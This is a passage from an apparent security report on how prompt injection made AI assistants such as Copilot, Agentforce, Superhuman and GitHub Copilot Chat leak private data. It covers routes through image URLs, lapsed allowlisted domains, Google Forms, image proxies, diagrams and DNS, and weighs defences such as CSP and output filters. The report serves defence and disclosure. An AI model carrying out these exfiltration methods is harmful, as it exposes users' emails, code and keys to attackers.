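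The other two exits reflect Copilot's growing abilities. EchoLeak had to use the displayed answer because Copilot could not send email on its own. By 2026 Copilot could also create files and run code, and Faisal observes that each new ability became a new way for data to leave. Even if Microsoft had repaired every fault in the display, new abilities could still have given data more ways out.

### What a control on the display can cover

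If Copilot's renderer had never loaded images from addresses the model wrote, it would have prevented EchoLeak, SearchLeak and ReLeak's exfiltration through Bing. The browser would not have requested the image, so the late sanitizer and the relay would not have mattered.

The same renderer would not have helped with the files or the sandbox, because the data in those cases never passed through the display. The answer on the screen could have been an ordinary summary, as it usually was in Lan and colleagues' experiments.

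Each of those exits needs its own rule. The program that writes a Word file could remove outside addresses, or the service that processes the file could refuse to fetch them. People legitimately put links in documents, so the first rule would annoy users more. The sandbox needs an effective block on network traffic. Different teams probably maintain these programs, and none of them can vouch for the others. Meeting Anderson's requirement that a check always be invoked therefore starts with a list of exits, which somebody has to update before Copilot gains a new ability. The list also has to include other Microsoft programs that display what an agent writes, such as the inbox where Copilot Cowork could get images displayed.

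In all three ReLeak cases, the final request, which reached the attacker, came from Microsoft's own servers. A customer's firewall could have detected at most an employee's browser contacting Bing. Microsoft could see all of these requests, but it can't simply forbid its servers to contact unknown sites, because Bing would stop working. To use a single rule for outgoing traffic, Microsoft would have to distinguish the requests caused by Copilot's output from all the others, which means keeping a label on that output as it passes from one service to the next.

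Controls on what the model reads work regardless of how the data would leave. Microsoft's optional rule that keeps outside email away from Copilot should stop all three ReLeak attacks when the email comes from outside the organisation. It would not have stopped SearchLeak, because those instructions came in a link. The Next Web also recommends tighter permissions, so that Copilot indexes fewer files and messages. This reduces what an attacker can take, even by a route that nobody has discovered yet.

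## Lists of allowed sites: Salesforce Agentforce and Superhuman

During EchoLeak and SearchLeak, the browser contacted only sites that Microsoft had allowed in Copilot's content security policy (CSP), but services on those sites passed the data on. Lists at two other companies failed for different reasons. Salesforce's policy included a domain whose registration had expired, so anyone could buy it. Superhuman, an email program, allowed a Google domain where anyone can create a form and collect the answers.

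Neither failure was a fault in the browser. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), a working draft from the main standards body for the web, specifies how a browser must apply a list of allowed sites. It describes CSP as an extra layer of defence, not a replacement for cleaning the text that goes into a page.

### How a browser applies the policy

A website normally sends its CSP in a header, a line of information that arrives before the page. The site can instead write the policy into the page, but the browser then applies the policy only to the content that comes after it. If a site sends no policy, the browser restricts nothing.

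A policy consists of directives, each of which has a name and usually a list of permitted sources. This one would suit a simple chat page (the addresses are placeholders):

```
Content-Security-Policy:
  default-src 'none';
  script-src 'self';
  style-src 'self';
  connect-src 'self';
  img-src https://images.example.com/chat/;
  form-action 'none';
  base-uri 'none'
```

| Line | Effect |
|---|---|
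| `default-src 'none'` | The browser loads no resource of any kind unless a later line permits it. |
| `script-src 'self'` | Programs can come only from the site that sent the page. |
| `style-src 'self'` | So can the files that set fonts and colours. |
| `connect-src 'self'` | Programs on the page can exchange data only with that site, which they must do to send the user's question. |
| `img-src https://images.example.com/chat/` | Images can come only from one folder on one host, over an encrypted connection. |
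| `form-action 'none'` | The page can't submit a form to any site. |
| `base-uri 'none'` | Nothing in the page can change which site its abbreviated addresses refer to. |

The image rule is the main defense against the leaks in this report, but a policy also needs a default rule, which covers every type of resource that has no rule of its own. W3C gives the example of a policy that bans images, scripts and fonts but has no default. Data can still leave through other requests, such as a prefetch, which a browser makes early for a resource that will probably be needed. A more specific rule replaces the default for its type of resource, so a site that sets the default to "none" but allows images from everywhere has no protection against image leaks. In general, W3C says, a policy prevents exfiltration only as well as its loosest list does.

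The browser checks an image's address against an entry by comparing the scheme (such as `https`), host, port and path. An entry can omit some of these parts, so `https:` on its own matches every encrypted site. An asterisk in front of a domain, as in `*.example.com`, matches every host under that domain, including hosts created after the developer wrote the policy. Eleven entries on Copilot's list in 2025 used an asterisk this way.

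When the browser checks an address against a CSP, it ignores the query, the part after the question mark. An entry whose path ends in a slash permits a whole folder, and any other path permits one file. Even an entry for a single picture lets the page attach any text to the request as a query, which is where a leaking address usually carries its data. A CSP therefore limits which sites can receive data, but not what the page sends them.

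If a permitted host redirects an image request, the browser checks the new address against the list before following it, and stops if the new host isn't there. By then the permitted host has already received the original address. The browser also ignores paths after a redirect, so an entry for one folder then permits the whole host. W3C accepted this loss of precision because a hostile page could otherwise try one path after another in its own policy and learn from the blocked requests where another site redirects its visitors.

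A page can have several policies, and a request must satisfy all of them. Adding a policy can therefore only tighten the restrictions. This helps against prompt injection because an attacker who got a new policy into the page could not use it to permit another site.

The browser can also report violations to the site's owner. A second, report-only header lets developers test a policy without blocking anything, but a site that uses only this header is unprotected. On a chat page, a sudden series of blocked images is good evidence of an attempted leak. The reports need careful handling because they include the blocked image's address, which may contain the private text. W3C warns developers to treat the reports as data that an attacker controls.

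### What the policy does not govern

A CSP doesn't restrict ordinary links, so if the user clicks a link in an answer, the browser goes to that address whether or not the site is on any list. The policy can restrict where forms send data and which sites may embed the page, but W3C's draft has no directive for links.

*The CSP navigate-to Directive* describes a rule that would have listed the sites a page could send its visitors to, but browsers never put it into general use. W3C's editors deleted it in the autumn of 2022. According to an engineer's 2022 comment on WebKit Bugzilla, the public bug tracker for Safari's browser engine, few browser makers supported it. Chrome's developers had built a version that was off by default, but they also wanted the directive removed. Website operators who want to prevent one-click leaks therefore have to remove or check the links themselves.

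Browser extensions are also exempt. W3C reasons that a user's choice to install an extension should take priority over the site owner's wishes. A page's policies may therefore not apply to an assistant that runs there as an extension.

A phone or desktop app enforces a CSP only if it displays answers in an embedded browser and its makers supply a policy. The policy never covers requests from the provider's own servers.

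### Salesforce's lapsed domain

Agentforce is a set of AI agents inside Salesforce, the software companies use to keep records of customers and sales. Many of these companies have a Web-to-Lead form on their websites, where a stranger can ask to be contacted. What the stranger types becomes a record in Salesforce, and an employee may later ask Agentforce about it.

In the attack Noma Security named ForcedLeak, the stranger's text contained instructions. When the employee asked about the record, Agentforce followed them and put customers' email addresses into an image's URL. The Hacker News (2025) quotes Noma, which blamed weak checks on what entered the model's context, a model that followed instructions too readily, and a way to bypass the CSP. Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* gives the flaw a severity of 9.4 out of 10.

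Salesforce had a CSP that blocked images from untrusted sites. But Willison (2025) explains that the policy still contained an asterisk entry for an expired Salesforce-related domain, which Noma's researchers then registered. Companies pay for a domain name for a fixed period, and if they stop paying, it eventually goes back on sale. The asterisk allowed requests to any host name under the domain, and the new owner could receive all of them.

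Encryption would not have helped. When an encrypted connection begins, the server presents a certificate proving that its operator controls the domain name. This protects against impostors, but the buyer of a lapsed domain does control it and can obtain a valid certificate.

The domain may well have gone unnoticed because nobody was using it. If Salesforce's pages had still loaded images from it, those images would have disappeared when the domain lapsed, and somebody would probably have complained. An unused entry leads to no complaints, and to no violation reports either, because browsers report only the requests they block. Saltzer and Schroeder's case for lists of permissions holds only for missing entries, because an entry that somebody forgot to remove is as hard to notice as a gap in a blocklist.

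### The repair and its cost

Noma told Salesforce about the flaw on 28 July 2025, according to ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection*, and Salesforce acknowledged it three days later. Salesforce regained control of the domain, which closed the route Noma had used. On 8 September it also began enforcing a list of Trusted URLs on its agents' output. Noma published its findings on 25 September.

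The second change is an output filter. In *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk*, PromptArmor, which monitors AI products for security flaws, describes how the filter works in Agentforce's chat inside the Salesforce web app. Before the app displays an answer, it replaces every address that isn't on the trusted list with a fixed label marking the removal, whether the address is in an image, a link, HTML, or a style rule. Because it also removes links, the filter blocks the one-click route that a CSP leaves open.

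The filter still depends on a list, and each customer has to maintain part of it. TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* reports that the change was mandatory and that administrators had to add every outside domain their agents needed or face disruption. An administrator facing a deadline has a reason to add broad entries and little reason to remove any later. PromptArmor advises against wildcard entries that cover sites where strangers can publish, and against allowing images from a trusted domain unless the agent must show them.

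Administrators use one settings page to choose which domains the filter trusts and which domains the CSP allows images from. This makes the list easier to maintain, but it also means the two layers don't fail independently. If an administrator trusts a bad domain and permits images from it, an image that leaks data to that domain will pass both.

A strict list can also block links it is meant to allow. One customer complained on Trailhead, Salesforce's training and community site, that Agentforce kept removing links to the company's own help articles even after an administrator had added all the relevant domains to the list. This is a single complaint about a test system, and a configuration mistake may have caused the problem. Still, an administrator in that position is likely to be tempted to loosen the list until the links work.

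PromptArmor says that removing addresses deals with only part of Agentforce's exposure, since an agent that can use tools may have other ways to send data. A year after ForcedLeak, researchers demonstrated one with SalesBleed, a set of weaknesses that let data out through the domain name system (DNS), as Poireault (2026) reports in *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk*. Before contacting a server, a computer looks up the server's numerical address in DNS, and the query normally reaches a name server chosen by the domain's owner. Text inside the domain name can therefore reach that owner even if no image loads and no page opens.

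SalesBleed began with Web-to-Lead, as ForcedLeak had, and needed no click. 三村 (2026), in *Salesforce Agentforceの「SalesBleed」脆弱性*, adds that Zenity Labs disclosed the weaknesses, that Salesforce has fixed them, and that an attacker could also have made Agentforce post phishing messages in Slack. The 2025 fix for ForcedLeak had restricted which web addresses an answer could contain, but it left strangers' text in the same channel as the employee's question, so an attacker needed only another way to send data out.

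### Superhuman and the Google form

Superhuman's list allowed images from the domain that hosts Google Docs, which Google still owned. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* explains that Google Forms uses the same domain, and that a form can accept an answer written into a web address. An attacker could create a form and get Superhuman's assistant to write an image address that would submit private text to the form. When the browser requested the image, Google stored the text as an answer the attacker could read.

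As in EchoLeak, the instructions arrived in an unopened email, which the assistant read when the user asked for a summary of recent mail. In PromptArmor's tests, one answer leaked the full contents of several sensitive emails, and another leaked parts of more than 40.

Google Forms worked as intended by collecting what was submitted. It was a relay in the sense used in this report, although it didn't forward anything. The data stayed on Google's servers, on the permitted domain, and the attacker logged in to read it. A check for services that redirect visitors or fetch addresses, the two functions that had caused trouble at Microsoft, would have missed a service that only stores text.

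Superhuman could have avoided this by permitting less of the domain. A CSP entry can include a path, so a developer who needs pictures from one service on a large shared domain can try to permit that service alone. This is better than listing the whole host, but the developer must know how another company organises its addresses and notice when that changes. W3C says that lists of hosts and paths are hard to get right on sprawling domains. Bing Chat's developers had an easier task because their list was short and contained only Bing's own hosts.

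Repairing the list alone would not have fixed two other weaknesses. Superhuman Go, a newer assistant that could read web pages and connected mailboxes, displayed images directly from an attacker's site. In Superhuman Mail, the assistant could open any web address while searching for information, so data could leave without an image, and the CSP did not apply to those requests.

PromptArmor reported its first findings on the night of Friday 5 December 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on Monday and released a first fix on Tuesday. It released further fixes on 18 December and, after a second report, on 11 January 2026, the day before PromptArmor published its account. PromptArmor doesn't say whether Superhuman removed the Google domain from its policy. Superhuman was much quicker than Microsoft was with EchoLeak, largely because it switched features off before working out how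 to fix them. That is easier to do with a new feature in an email program than with one that large organisations already depend on.

The same flaw turned up elsewhere after it was made public. On 21 April 2026, just over three months later, PromptArmor reported to OpenAI that Codex, OpenAI's agent for coding and other work, could send a user's emails to a Google Form through an image. OpenAI has fixed the flaw. Google's documents domain is easy to approve because so many people use it for ordinary work and don't associate it with attackers.

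### Who sets the policy: Dify and Rovo

Salesforce and Superhuman had lists of allowed sites, but the chat front end of Dify, an open-source platform that companies use to build and run their own chatbots, applied no image policy by default, according to a December 2025 report. Without such a policy, a browser will load an image from any site specified in the model's output.

This arrangement makes it easy to lose track of who is responsible. Dify's developers write the page but don't know which image hosts each company will need. The company that installs Dify knows this but may assume a finished product comes with suitable protection. A safer default would allow images only from the chatbot's own site until a company added other hosts.

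Atlassian's Rovo is an assistant that works across the company's products, including Jira, which tracks tasks, and Confluence, which stores an organisation's documents. An administrator can switch off Rovo's web search for the whole organisation. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* reports that this did not prevent a zero-click leak, because the setting stopped the searches but not all of Rovo's requests to outside sites. A user who returned to the conversation later would see only an ordinary answer.

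PromptArmor reported the flaw to Atlassian on 23 May 2026. It published its findings more than two months later, saying that Atlassian had stopped replying and that Rovo was still vulnerable. The flaw may still be open, so organisations can't rely on the setting to keep data in until Atlassian confirms a repair. They can, however, limit which documents and connected services Rovo can read.

Atlassian's setting turned off web search, as its name suggests, but an administrator could easily mistake it for a control on all outside contact, much as the programmers at MIT assumed that a check on data in transit protected the whole transfer. Microsoft's *Control image rendering and embedded URLs* describes a setting with a better name. In Copilot Studio, where companies build their own agents, an administrator can stop answers from showing images and clickable links, and Microsoft gives preventing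 data exfiltration as a reason. An administrator can tell from the name which routes the setting covers, and it is fairly clear that other requests need a separate control.

### What a list of names can guarantee

A CSP's image rule guarantees only that a browser enforcing it will limit the page's image requests to hosts whose names match the list. To conclude that no outsider receives private data through an image, the site's owner also has to know that every listed name still leads to a server run by somebody trustworthy, and that the server won't forward the data or store it where an outsider can read it. The browser can't check either condition. Salesforce was wrong about who controlled a name, and Superhuman was wrong about what a service did with the text it received.

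Each entry added to a list of allowed sites increases the chance that one of them will become unsafe. Suppose, for illustration, that each entry has an independent 1 per cent chance per year of becoming unsafe, through a lapsed registration or a new feature. By the same calculation as for repeated attacks on a model, the chance of at least one new unsafe entry within a year is about 4 per cent for the four hosts on Bing Chat's list and about 25 per cent for the 29 entries on Copilot's. Real entries are not independent, since one company may run several of them, and an asterisk entry stands for an unknown number of hosts. But the risk still grows with the number of entries, and a list that was safe when written needs regular review because its entries can become unsafe later.

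Different people have to do that work:

| Duty | Who has to do it | Where its absence mattered |
|---|---|---|
| Record the reason for each entry and delete the entry when the reason no longer applies | The team that runs the page | Salesforce |
| Keep renewing a domain until every policy has dropped it | Whoever manages the company's domains | Salesforce |
| Find out what each permitted service does with text in an address, and ask again when the service changes | The page's team, with help from the service's team | Superhuman, Copilot |
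| Supply a restrictive policy with the product | The product's developers | Dify |
| Test whether a setting stops every request that administrators would expect it to stop | The product's developers | Rovo |

A program can easily check the registration of every listed domain each night and warn the company weeks before one expires. Outsiders can run the same check, and a company should assume that attackers do. Discovering that a respectable service also accepts and stores text is much harder to automate, because a person has to understand what the service is for.

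The simplest way to reduce the work is to use a separate image host, as suggested above for Copilot. If the host also accepts no submissions, the page's owner has only one entry to watch. The host's request logs still need protection because they could contain private text. This design blocks images from the open web, which is a real loss for some products, and showing a warning in place of each missing picture would not be much better. OpenAI objects to strict site lists partly for that reason.

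### Connection Allowlists

Google has been developing a browser mechanism that would close some of the gaps in CSP. *Connection Allowlists* proposes a single list of allowed destinations for all of a page's connections, whatever their type. Mike West of Google, who wrote the proposal and is also an editor of the CSP specification, argues that dividing requests into images, fonts, scripts and so on is the wrong approach to data exfiltration, since a leak through a font does as much harm as a leak through an image. He also points out that CSP never fully covered some kinds of connection, including early DNS lookups and WebRTC, which browsers use for live calls.

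The website sends the list in a dedicated header, and the browser checks each destination against it before opening a connection. Chrome for Developers' *Connection Allowlists origin trial* (2026) says that the check also covers navigation from one page to another, for which the CSP directive was removed in 2022. It lists generative AI as one of the main uses, particularly on sites that run model-written code. The security researcher Helme explains that the list applies to the whole document, so it doesn't matter what started the connection.

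West's draft blocks every redirected request, even if the new destination is on the list, but this rule is not settled. It prevents leaks through redirects but would break many ordinary websites, as West acknowledges, and the draft sets out several looser rules that could replace it. The list also applies to a single page, not the whole site, so an attacker who can run code on the page might reach another page of the same site that has a weaker list.

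A broader check requires more entries to maintain. Chrome for Developers' *FedCM* (2026) warns that a strict list can block sign-in through an outside identity service unless the site's owner adds that service's addresses. An owner who adds them must trust another outside company with whatever the page might send.

A related proposal, *Intent to Prototype*, a notice by Microsoft engineer Maslen, would let a page impose a list of allowed connections on the content it embeds. This could help when one company's assistant runs inside another company's page, because the host would not have to rely on the assistant's developers to set a list.

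Connection Allowlists would not have prevented the failures at Salesforce or Superhuman if the same domains had been on the list. More generally, according to West's draft, any mechanism based on names fails if a name leads to an unexpected server. A browser's list also can't restrict requests from the provider's servers. Such a list would help most where a company had chosen its destinations well but forgotten one type of request.

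The mechanism is available mainly in Chrome. Google began a public trial with Chrome 148 and introduced the feature in Chrome 152 in August 2026, where Chrome Platform Status lists it as an ordinary feature rather than a trial. It isn't a W3C standard or on the way to becoming one. When Toreini reviewed the design for W3C in February 2026, the comments were favourable about the goal but noted that no other browser maker had taken a position. CentralCSP's *Connection Allowlists, a network egress sandbox in the browser*, written before Chrome 152, reported no sign of support from Firefox or Safari and advised sites to test the feature without depending on it. A chatbot's makers can send the new header to protect Chrome users, but they still need a CSP for everyone else.

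## Image proxies and image blocking: GitHub Copilot Chat and other coding assistants

An image proxy fetches images on the reader's behalf, so a website can show images from anywhere while its content security policy (CSP) permits only one image host. GitHub has run a proxy called Camo for more than twelve years, and Gmail and some other email services run similar ones. These proxies protect readers from the owner of the image's host, but they are worse at stopping an assistant from leaking data. In 2025, a security researcher used Camo to get private code out of GitHub Copilot Chat.

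### How Camo works

GitHub built Camo because browsers displayed warnings when an encrypted page contained unencrypted images (GitHub, *Sidejack Prevention Phase 3*). It later extended Camo to encrypted images to hide readers' browser details from other companies and make pages load faster (GitHub, *Proxying User Images*, 2014).

An outside image in a comment, or in the README file that introduces a project, reaches the reader in six steps:

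1. GitHub's server converts the Markdown to HTML and replaces the image's address with an address at the proxy.
2. The new address includes the old one, in encoded form, and a signature.
3. The reader's browser requests the new address, which GitHub's CSP permits because the proxy is on a domain that GitHub owns.
4. The proxy checks the signature and refuses the request if it is wrong.
5. The proxy fetches the picture from its original host, checks its type and size, and sends it to the browser.
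6. GitHub keeps a copy for later readers, unless the image's host has asked it not to.

The new address has this general form (the host is a placeholder):

`https://proxy.example/SIGNATURE/ORIGINAL-ADDRESS`

The signature is an HMAC, a short code that a program calculates from a message and a secret key. If *u* is the original address and *k* is a key that only GitHub's servers hold, the signature is

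*s* = HMAC(*k*, *u*).

The proxy recalculates the signature *s* from the address *u* and the key *k*, then compares the result with the signature it received. Nobody without *k* can work out the signature for a new address, and changing one character of *u* makes the old signature invalid. The Microsoft services that acted as relays for Copilot had no such check.

GitHub signs the address of any outside image its users post, so a valid signature shows that GitHub has processed the address, not that it trusts the host. According to the notes published with the code for GitHub's image proxy, *camo*, the reason for signing is to let the company clear stored copies, ban abusers and limit the number of requests. By default, camo also follows up to four redirects, so the image may come from an address that GitHub has not signed.

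The proxy itself needs upkeep because it handles untrusted files. GitHub (2014) reports that Camo checked only the beginning of a file's declared type to decide whether it was an image, so an attacker could pass off a web page as an image and run code on the proxy's domain. GitHub replaced the check with a list of exact types and moved the proxy to a domain separate from its main site.

### What a proxy hides

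Email services adopted proxies because advertisers use invisible images to find out who reads their messages. The table shows what the owner of the server hosting an image can see in each arrangement. Cookies are small pieces of data that a site uses to recognise a returning browser.

| | No proxy | Proxy fetches when the reader opens the email | Proxy fetches when the email arrives |
|---|---|---|---|
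| Reader's network address | Visible | Hidden | Hidden |
| Cookies and device details | Visible | Hidden | Hidden |
| Text in the image's address | Visible | Visible | Visible |
| Time of reading | Visible | Visible, unless the proxy already has a copy | Hidden |

Gmail used to ask before showing outside images. In December 2013, *Images Now Showing* (Rae-Grant, 2013) announced that Gmail would display them automatically because they would now come through Google's servers. Valsorda tested this in *How the new Gmail image proxy works* (2013) by emailing himself a picture stored on his own server. The server received nothing when the email arrived. When he opened the email, the server received a request from Google, without his network address or browser name. A sender would not have learned those details but would have learned when he read the email. Google may have changed the proxy since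 then, but Google's *Turn images on or off in Gmail* still warns that senders may sometimes know whether somebody has opened an email.

An image proxy also passes on text in the image's address. Englehardt, Han and Narayanan (2018), in *I never signed up for this!*, collected 12,618 emails from 902 mailing lists and simulated a person reading them. About 29 per cent of the emails sent the reader's email address to at least one outside company, typically inside the address of an image. Englehardt and colleagues argue that a proxy makes such leaks harder to stop, because it replaces the tracker's name with its own, and mail programs block known trackers by name. A browser applying a CSP has the same difficulty, because every proxied image comes from one permitted host.

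An image proxy can keep a reader's location and browsing history from advertisers, but it doesn't by itself stop someone from stealing data through a chatbot. The stolen text is in the image's address, which the proxy passes on intact unless a rule such as Camo's signature check blocks it.

*SoK* (2018), a survey of email security, points out that fetching every picture as soon as an email arrives would hide when the user reads it. Apple's *Mail Privacy Protection & Privacy* describes a feature that does this in the background, whether or not the user opens the email. The requests pass through two servers run by different organisations, so that neither has both the user's network address and the email's remote content. However, Cardwell tested the feature on two iPhones and, in *Apple's "Protect Mail Activity" Doesn't Work*, disputes that Apple's Mail app fetches images early. Apple told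 him that the feature was working as expected. An outsider can check only by looking at the log of the server that holds the picture, as Valsorda did.

Proxies also break some legitimate images. Gmail's proxy can't show images stored on a company's internal network, or some that require the reader's cookies. Google's *Set up an image URL proxy allowlist* explains how administrators can exempt such addresses from the proxy, and advises them to consult their security team first. Someone also has to maintain this allowlist.

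### The first fix to Copilot Chat

GitHub Copilot Chat answers programmers' questions about code, either on GitHub's website or inside an editor such as Visual Studio Code (VS Code). In February 2024 Rehberger told GitHub that instructions planted in a file could make the VS Code version leak data through an image. According to Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat*, GitHub replied in March that it was already tracking the problem, and confirmed a fix on 12 June.

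Rehberger thought that the chat had stopped showing images altogether. Willison, in *GitHub Copilot Chat*, describes the fix as a ban on images from untrusted domains. An undated summary from GitHub's bug-bounty programme, reproduced in Vulners' *GitHub*, supports Willison's version, if it refers to the same report. Rehberger's observation is also compatible with a ban on untrusted domains, because an attacker's test image would have disappeared under either rule. According to the summary, GitHub also introduced warnings about links.

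The fix dealt with both zero-click and one-click leaks, though the warnings work only if people follow them. It also left GitHub to decide which domains to trust, and companies naturally trust their own domains.

### CamoLeak

In June 2025 a researcher at Legit Security, which sells tools for securing software development, found a leak in the version of Copilot Chat on GitHub's website. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* rates the leak's severity 9.6 out of 10 but does not identify who assigned the score. GitHub told the researcher that it had fixed the leak as of 14 August, and Nudge Security's *CamoLeak* (2025) dates the public disclosure to 8 October.

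The instructions arrived in a pull request, a proposed change to a project's code, which a stranger can submit if the project is public. Copilot works with the permissions of whoever is asking, so an employee who asked it to explain the pull request also gave it access to the employer's private projects. In the researcher's tests, Copilot leaked the description of an undisclosed security flaw from a private project and the results of a search for access keys.

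GitHub's CSP allowed images only from domains that GitHub owned, so it had none of the faults described in the previous section, such as a lapsed registration or an outside service that collected submissions. One permitted host, however, was Camo, which fetches images from the rest of the web. Camo correctly checked the signature on every request, but a request with a valid signature could still depend on private data that Copilot had read.

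GitHub once had good reason to rely on the signature. GitHub (2017) describes hiring the security company Cure53 to find out what attackers could do once they had inserted text into one of its pages. Cure53 showed that two outside services on GitHub's list of image hosts could pass a page's secrets to an attacker, so GitHub took both off the list. One of them supplied users' profile pictures. GitHub began fetching those through Camo instead, because its server knew each picture's address before it built the page. GitHub reasoned that an attacker would need to know a whole address in advance to have a signature for it, and so could not have one for an address containing a secret they had yet to learn.

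That argument covered inserted text that stays the same once the attacker has written it. A language model composes its answer after reading the secret, so the argument no longer covered everything that could happen on the page. As with Hardy's compiler, Camo's code was still correct but became unsafe when the system around it changed. The engineers who added the chat would have had to re-examine the 2017 argument to notice this.

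CamoLeak is also a reason to be cautious about the signed media proxy, which Reddy and Gujral credit in their table with stopping zero-click leaks. Their proxy is stricter than Camo because its approvals expire, but the protection any such proxy offers depends on who can get an approval and for what.

GitHub fixed the flaw by disabling images in the chat completely. Petri's *GitHub Copilot Chat Hit by ‘CamoLeak’ Flaw Allowing Silent Data Exfiltration* reports that GitHub also blocked the use of Camo to disclose users' content. Disabling images was sensible because it didn't require GitHub to anticipate the next way of misusing the proxy. Programmers seldom need images when they ask for an explanation of code, and comments and README files could still show them.

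### Four designs for showing images

GitHub's aim can be stated more exactly: requests to outside hosts should not depend on private data. Let *p* be the private data that the assistant can read, and let *R*(*p*) be the full record of the image requests that reach outside hosts, including their addresses, order and times. Nothing leaks through images if

*R*(*p*) = *R*(*p*′) for all possible *p* and *p*′,

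because then even somebody with the logs of every outside host could not tell one set of private data from another. Security researchers call this property noninterference. A developer who wants to come close to it has roughly four options.

| Design | Can outside requests depend on private data? | What users lose |
|---|---|---|
| No images | No, because there are none | All pictures in answers |
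| Images only from the product's own storage | No, if the storage never fetches anything | Pictures from the web that nobody has uploaded |
| A proxy that refuses addresses the model wrote | Yes, to a lesser extent | Charts from services that take the figures from the address |
| Fetching before the model sees private data | No, if the program fetches every picture by then | Pictures that the assistant finds later |

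A design that displays no images is the easiest to verify. The team that owns the renderer can remove the image-display code, but has to make sure later features don't bring it back. Links need a separate control.

Allowing images from the product's own storage lets the assistant show screenshots that users have uploaded and charts that the product has drawn. CamoLeak shows why the product shouldn't allow its whole domain. A CSP doesn't distinguish a host that only stores images from one that fetches them on request, and only the first kind belongs on the list. A company could still offer images from the web by copying them into storage when an author saves a document, before anyone asks the assistant about it, but the copies would go out of date. Many README files on GitHub include a badge showing whether the latest version of a program passes its tests, and a stored copy could show a pass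 long after the tests began to fail. GitHub's help page tells owners of changing images to turn off Camo's caching for much the same reason.

A proxy could refuse image addresses the model wrote and fetch only those from another source, such as a file the user had opened. The model then couldn't leak a password by writing it into an address. But a stranger may have written the file, and the model may still influence which requests go out and when. The program also has to keep a reliable record of where each address came from, and each approval should apply to only one conversation. ChatGPT used a similar check in early 2024, which accepted any address already in the conversation. Wu and colleagues bypassed it.

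Fetching images early means the program sends the requests before the model has anything private to reveal. Suppose a user wants to compare a public web page with a confidential report. The program downloads and stores every picture on the page before giving the model the report. Whatever the model writes afterwards, the program uses the stored copies and makes no new requests. It has to download all the pictures, including those the answer won't use, because a selection made later could depend on the report.

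It is hard to find a moment when the assistant has no private data. If the model reads the report and then opens a second web page, its choice of page may depend on the report. An assistant with a long-term memory, or one that starts inside a private code project, has private data from the first message. Early fetching therefore works better in a tool with fixed stages, such as one that gathers public sources and then combines them with internal documents, than in an open-ended chat.

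For an assistant that can read private code, the choice is between showing no images and showing only images from the product's own storage. The other two designs allow more images, but their maintainers have to get more things right.

### Diagrams

Blocking images in Markdown does not stop a program from loading them another way. Many coding assistants can draw diagrams from text written in Mermaid, a notation in which "User --> Computer" produces two boxes joined by an arrow. A diagram can also contain an image, which the program drawing it may fetch from the web. In 2025, Microsoft 365 Copilot and at least one coding assistant each had a leak through diagrams.

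In *Takedown*, Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025) at the South Korean university KAIST examined eight widely used coding agents, which can read files, run commands and change a project by themselves. The researchers recorded the messages between each agent and its model where they could, and read or reconstructed much of the agents' code. They found 15 security issues. By combining such issues, they could run any command on the user's computer with five of the agents, and take files from anywhere on the computer with four, without the user approving anything.

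The researchers tested how one agent displayed each notation it supported and found that it could leak data through diagrams, because the diagram renderer could load an outside image without asking the user. The agent could also read files outside the project it was working on. In the researchers' demonstration, a stranger's text in a project's issue tracker led the agent to send out a key stored elsewhere on the computer. Someone else had already reported the diagram flaw to the vendor. In a different agent, the tool for fetching web pages also needed no approval, so data could leave without passing through the display.

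Lee and colleagues withheld the products' names while the vendors worked on repairs, so readers can't tell which were affected. Several vendors considered some of the behaviour intended and declined to change it. The study is good evidence that these faults occurred in popular products in 2025, but eight products are too few to show how common the faults were.

Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE* describes how Rehberger found that diagrams drawn by the code editor Cursor could contact outside servers. The official record, MITRE's *CVE-2025-54132*, lists the flaw as fixed in version 1.3. Two months later, a second record, GCVE's *CVE-2025-61589* (2025), covered every version up to 1.6. According to CVELogic's *CVE-2025-61589*, the first fix had missed some cases, and SentinelOne's *CVE-2025-61589* says that version 1.7 fixed them.

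A rule that restricts requests applies whatever notation produced them, whereas a rule about image notation has to cover every notation that can lead to a request, including any that a diagram library adds in an update. For example, if an editor draws its chat panel with an embedded browser, its developers can give the panel a Content Security Policy (CSP) that permits no outside images. The browser will apply that policy to images in diagrams too, so nobody, including Cursor's developers, would need a complete list of what Mermaid can do.

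Rules about which requests to allow can also be implemented incorrectly. VS Code has a tool that fetches web pages for the assistant and asks the user first unless the site is on a trusted list. GitHub's *Safeguarding VS Code against prompt injections* reports that the code comparing addresses with this list was flawed. A CSP on the chat panel would not have blocked the resulting requests, because the tool is separate from the chat's display.

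### Continue and CodeGPT

More than a year after GitHub fixed Copilot Chat in VS Code, two other assistants for the same editor still had the image flaw. VerSprite, a security consultancy, reported it to both makers in August 2025.

VerSprite sent a report to the developers of Continue, an open-source assistant, on 20 August. They acknowledged it and released a corrected test version the next day, according to VerSprite's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue*. Continue now asks the user before loading an outside image and restricts access to certain files.

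Anthropic's 2023 fix for Claude also asked before each image, so it too relied on the user's judgement. Continue's fix is stronger because it also restricts which files the assistant can open. Projects often keep passwords and access keys in settings files. An assistant rarely needs these files to explain code, and if it can't open them, it can't leak their contents by any route.

According to VerSprite's *Another Day, Another Leak*, VerSprite contacted CodeGPT's makers on 21 August by email and through administrators of their online chat group, but they did not reply. VerSprite tested a new version released on 27 August and found the same flaw. Six days is a short time for a repair, so the new version alone is little evidence of the makers' intentions. The lack of any acknowledgement is more worrying, because users can't tell whether anybody is working on the problem.

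The flaw in CodeGPT may still be unfixed. VerSprite advises users not to use the assistant on sensitive projects until it is patched, and to be careful about asking it to analyse files from people they don't trust. A company can also limit which assistants its programmers install, since VS Code lets each assistant's developer decide how it displays answers.

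## Checking each address before it is fetched: ChatGPT and Claude

ChatGPT and Claude open web pages for their users, so OpenAI and Anthropic can't block everything from outside, as GitHub did with images. An assistant that looks up a train time or compares washing machines has to contact servers its developers have never heard of, and every request sends an address to one of them. Both companies apply a rule to each address before the assistant opens it. OpenAI's rule depends on whether the address was already public, and Anthropic's depends on how the address got into the conversation.

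### An index of public addresses

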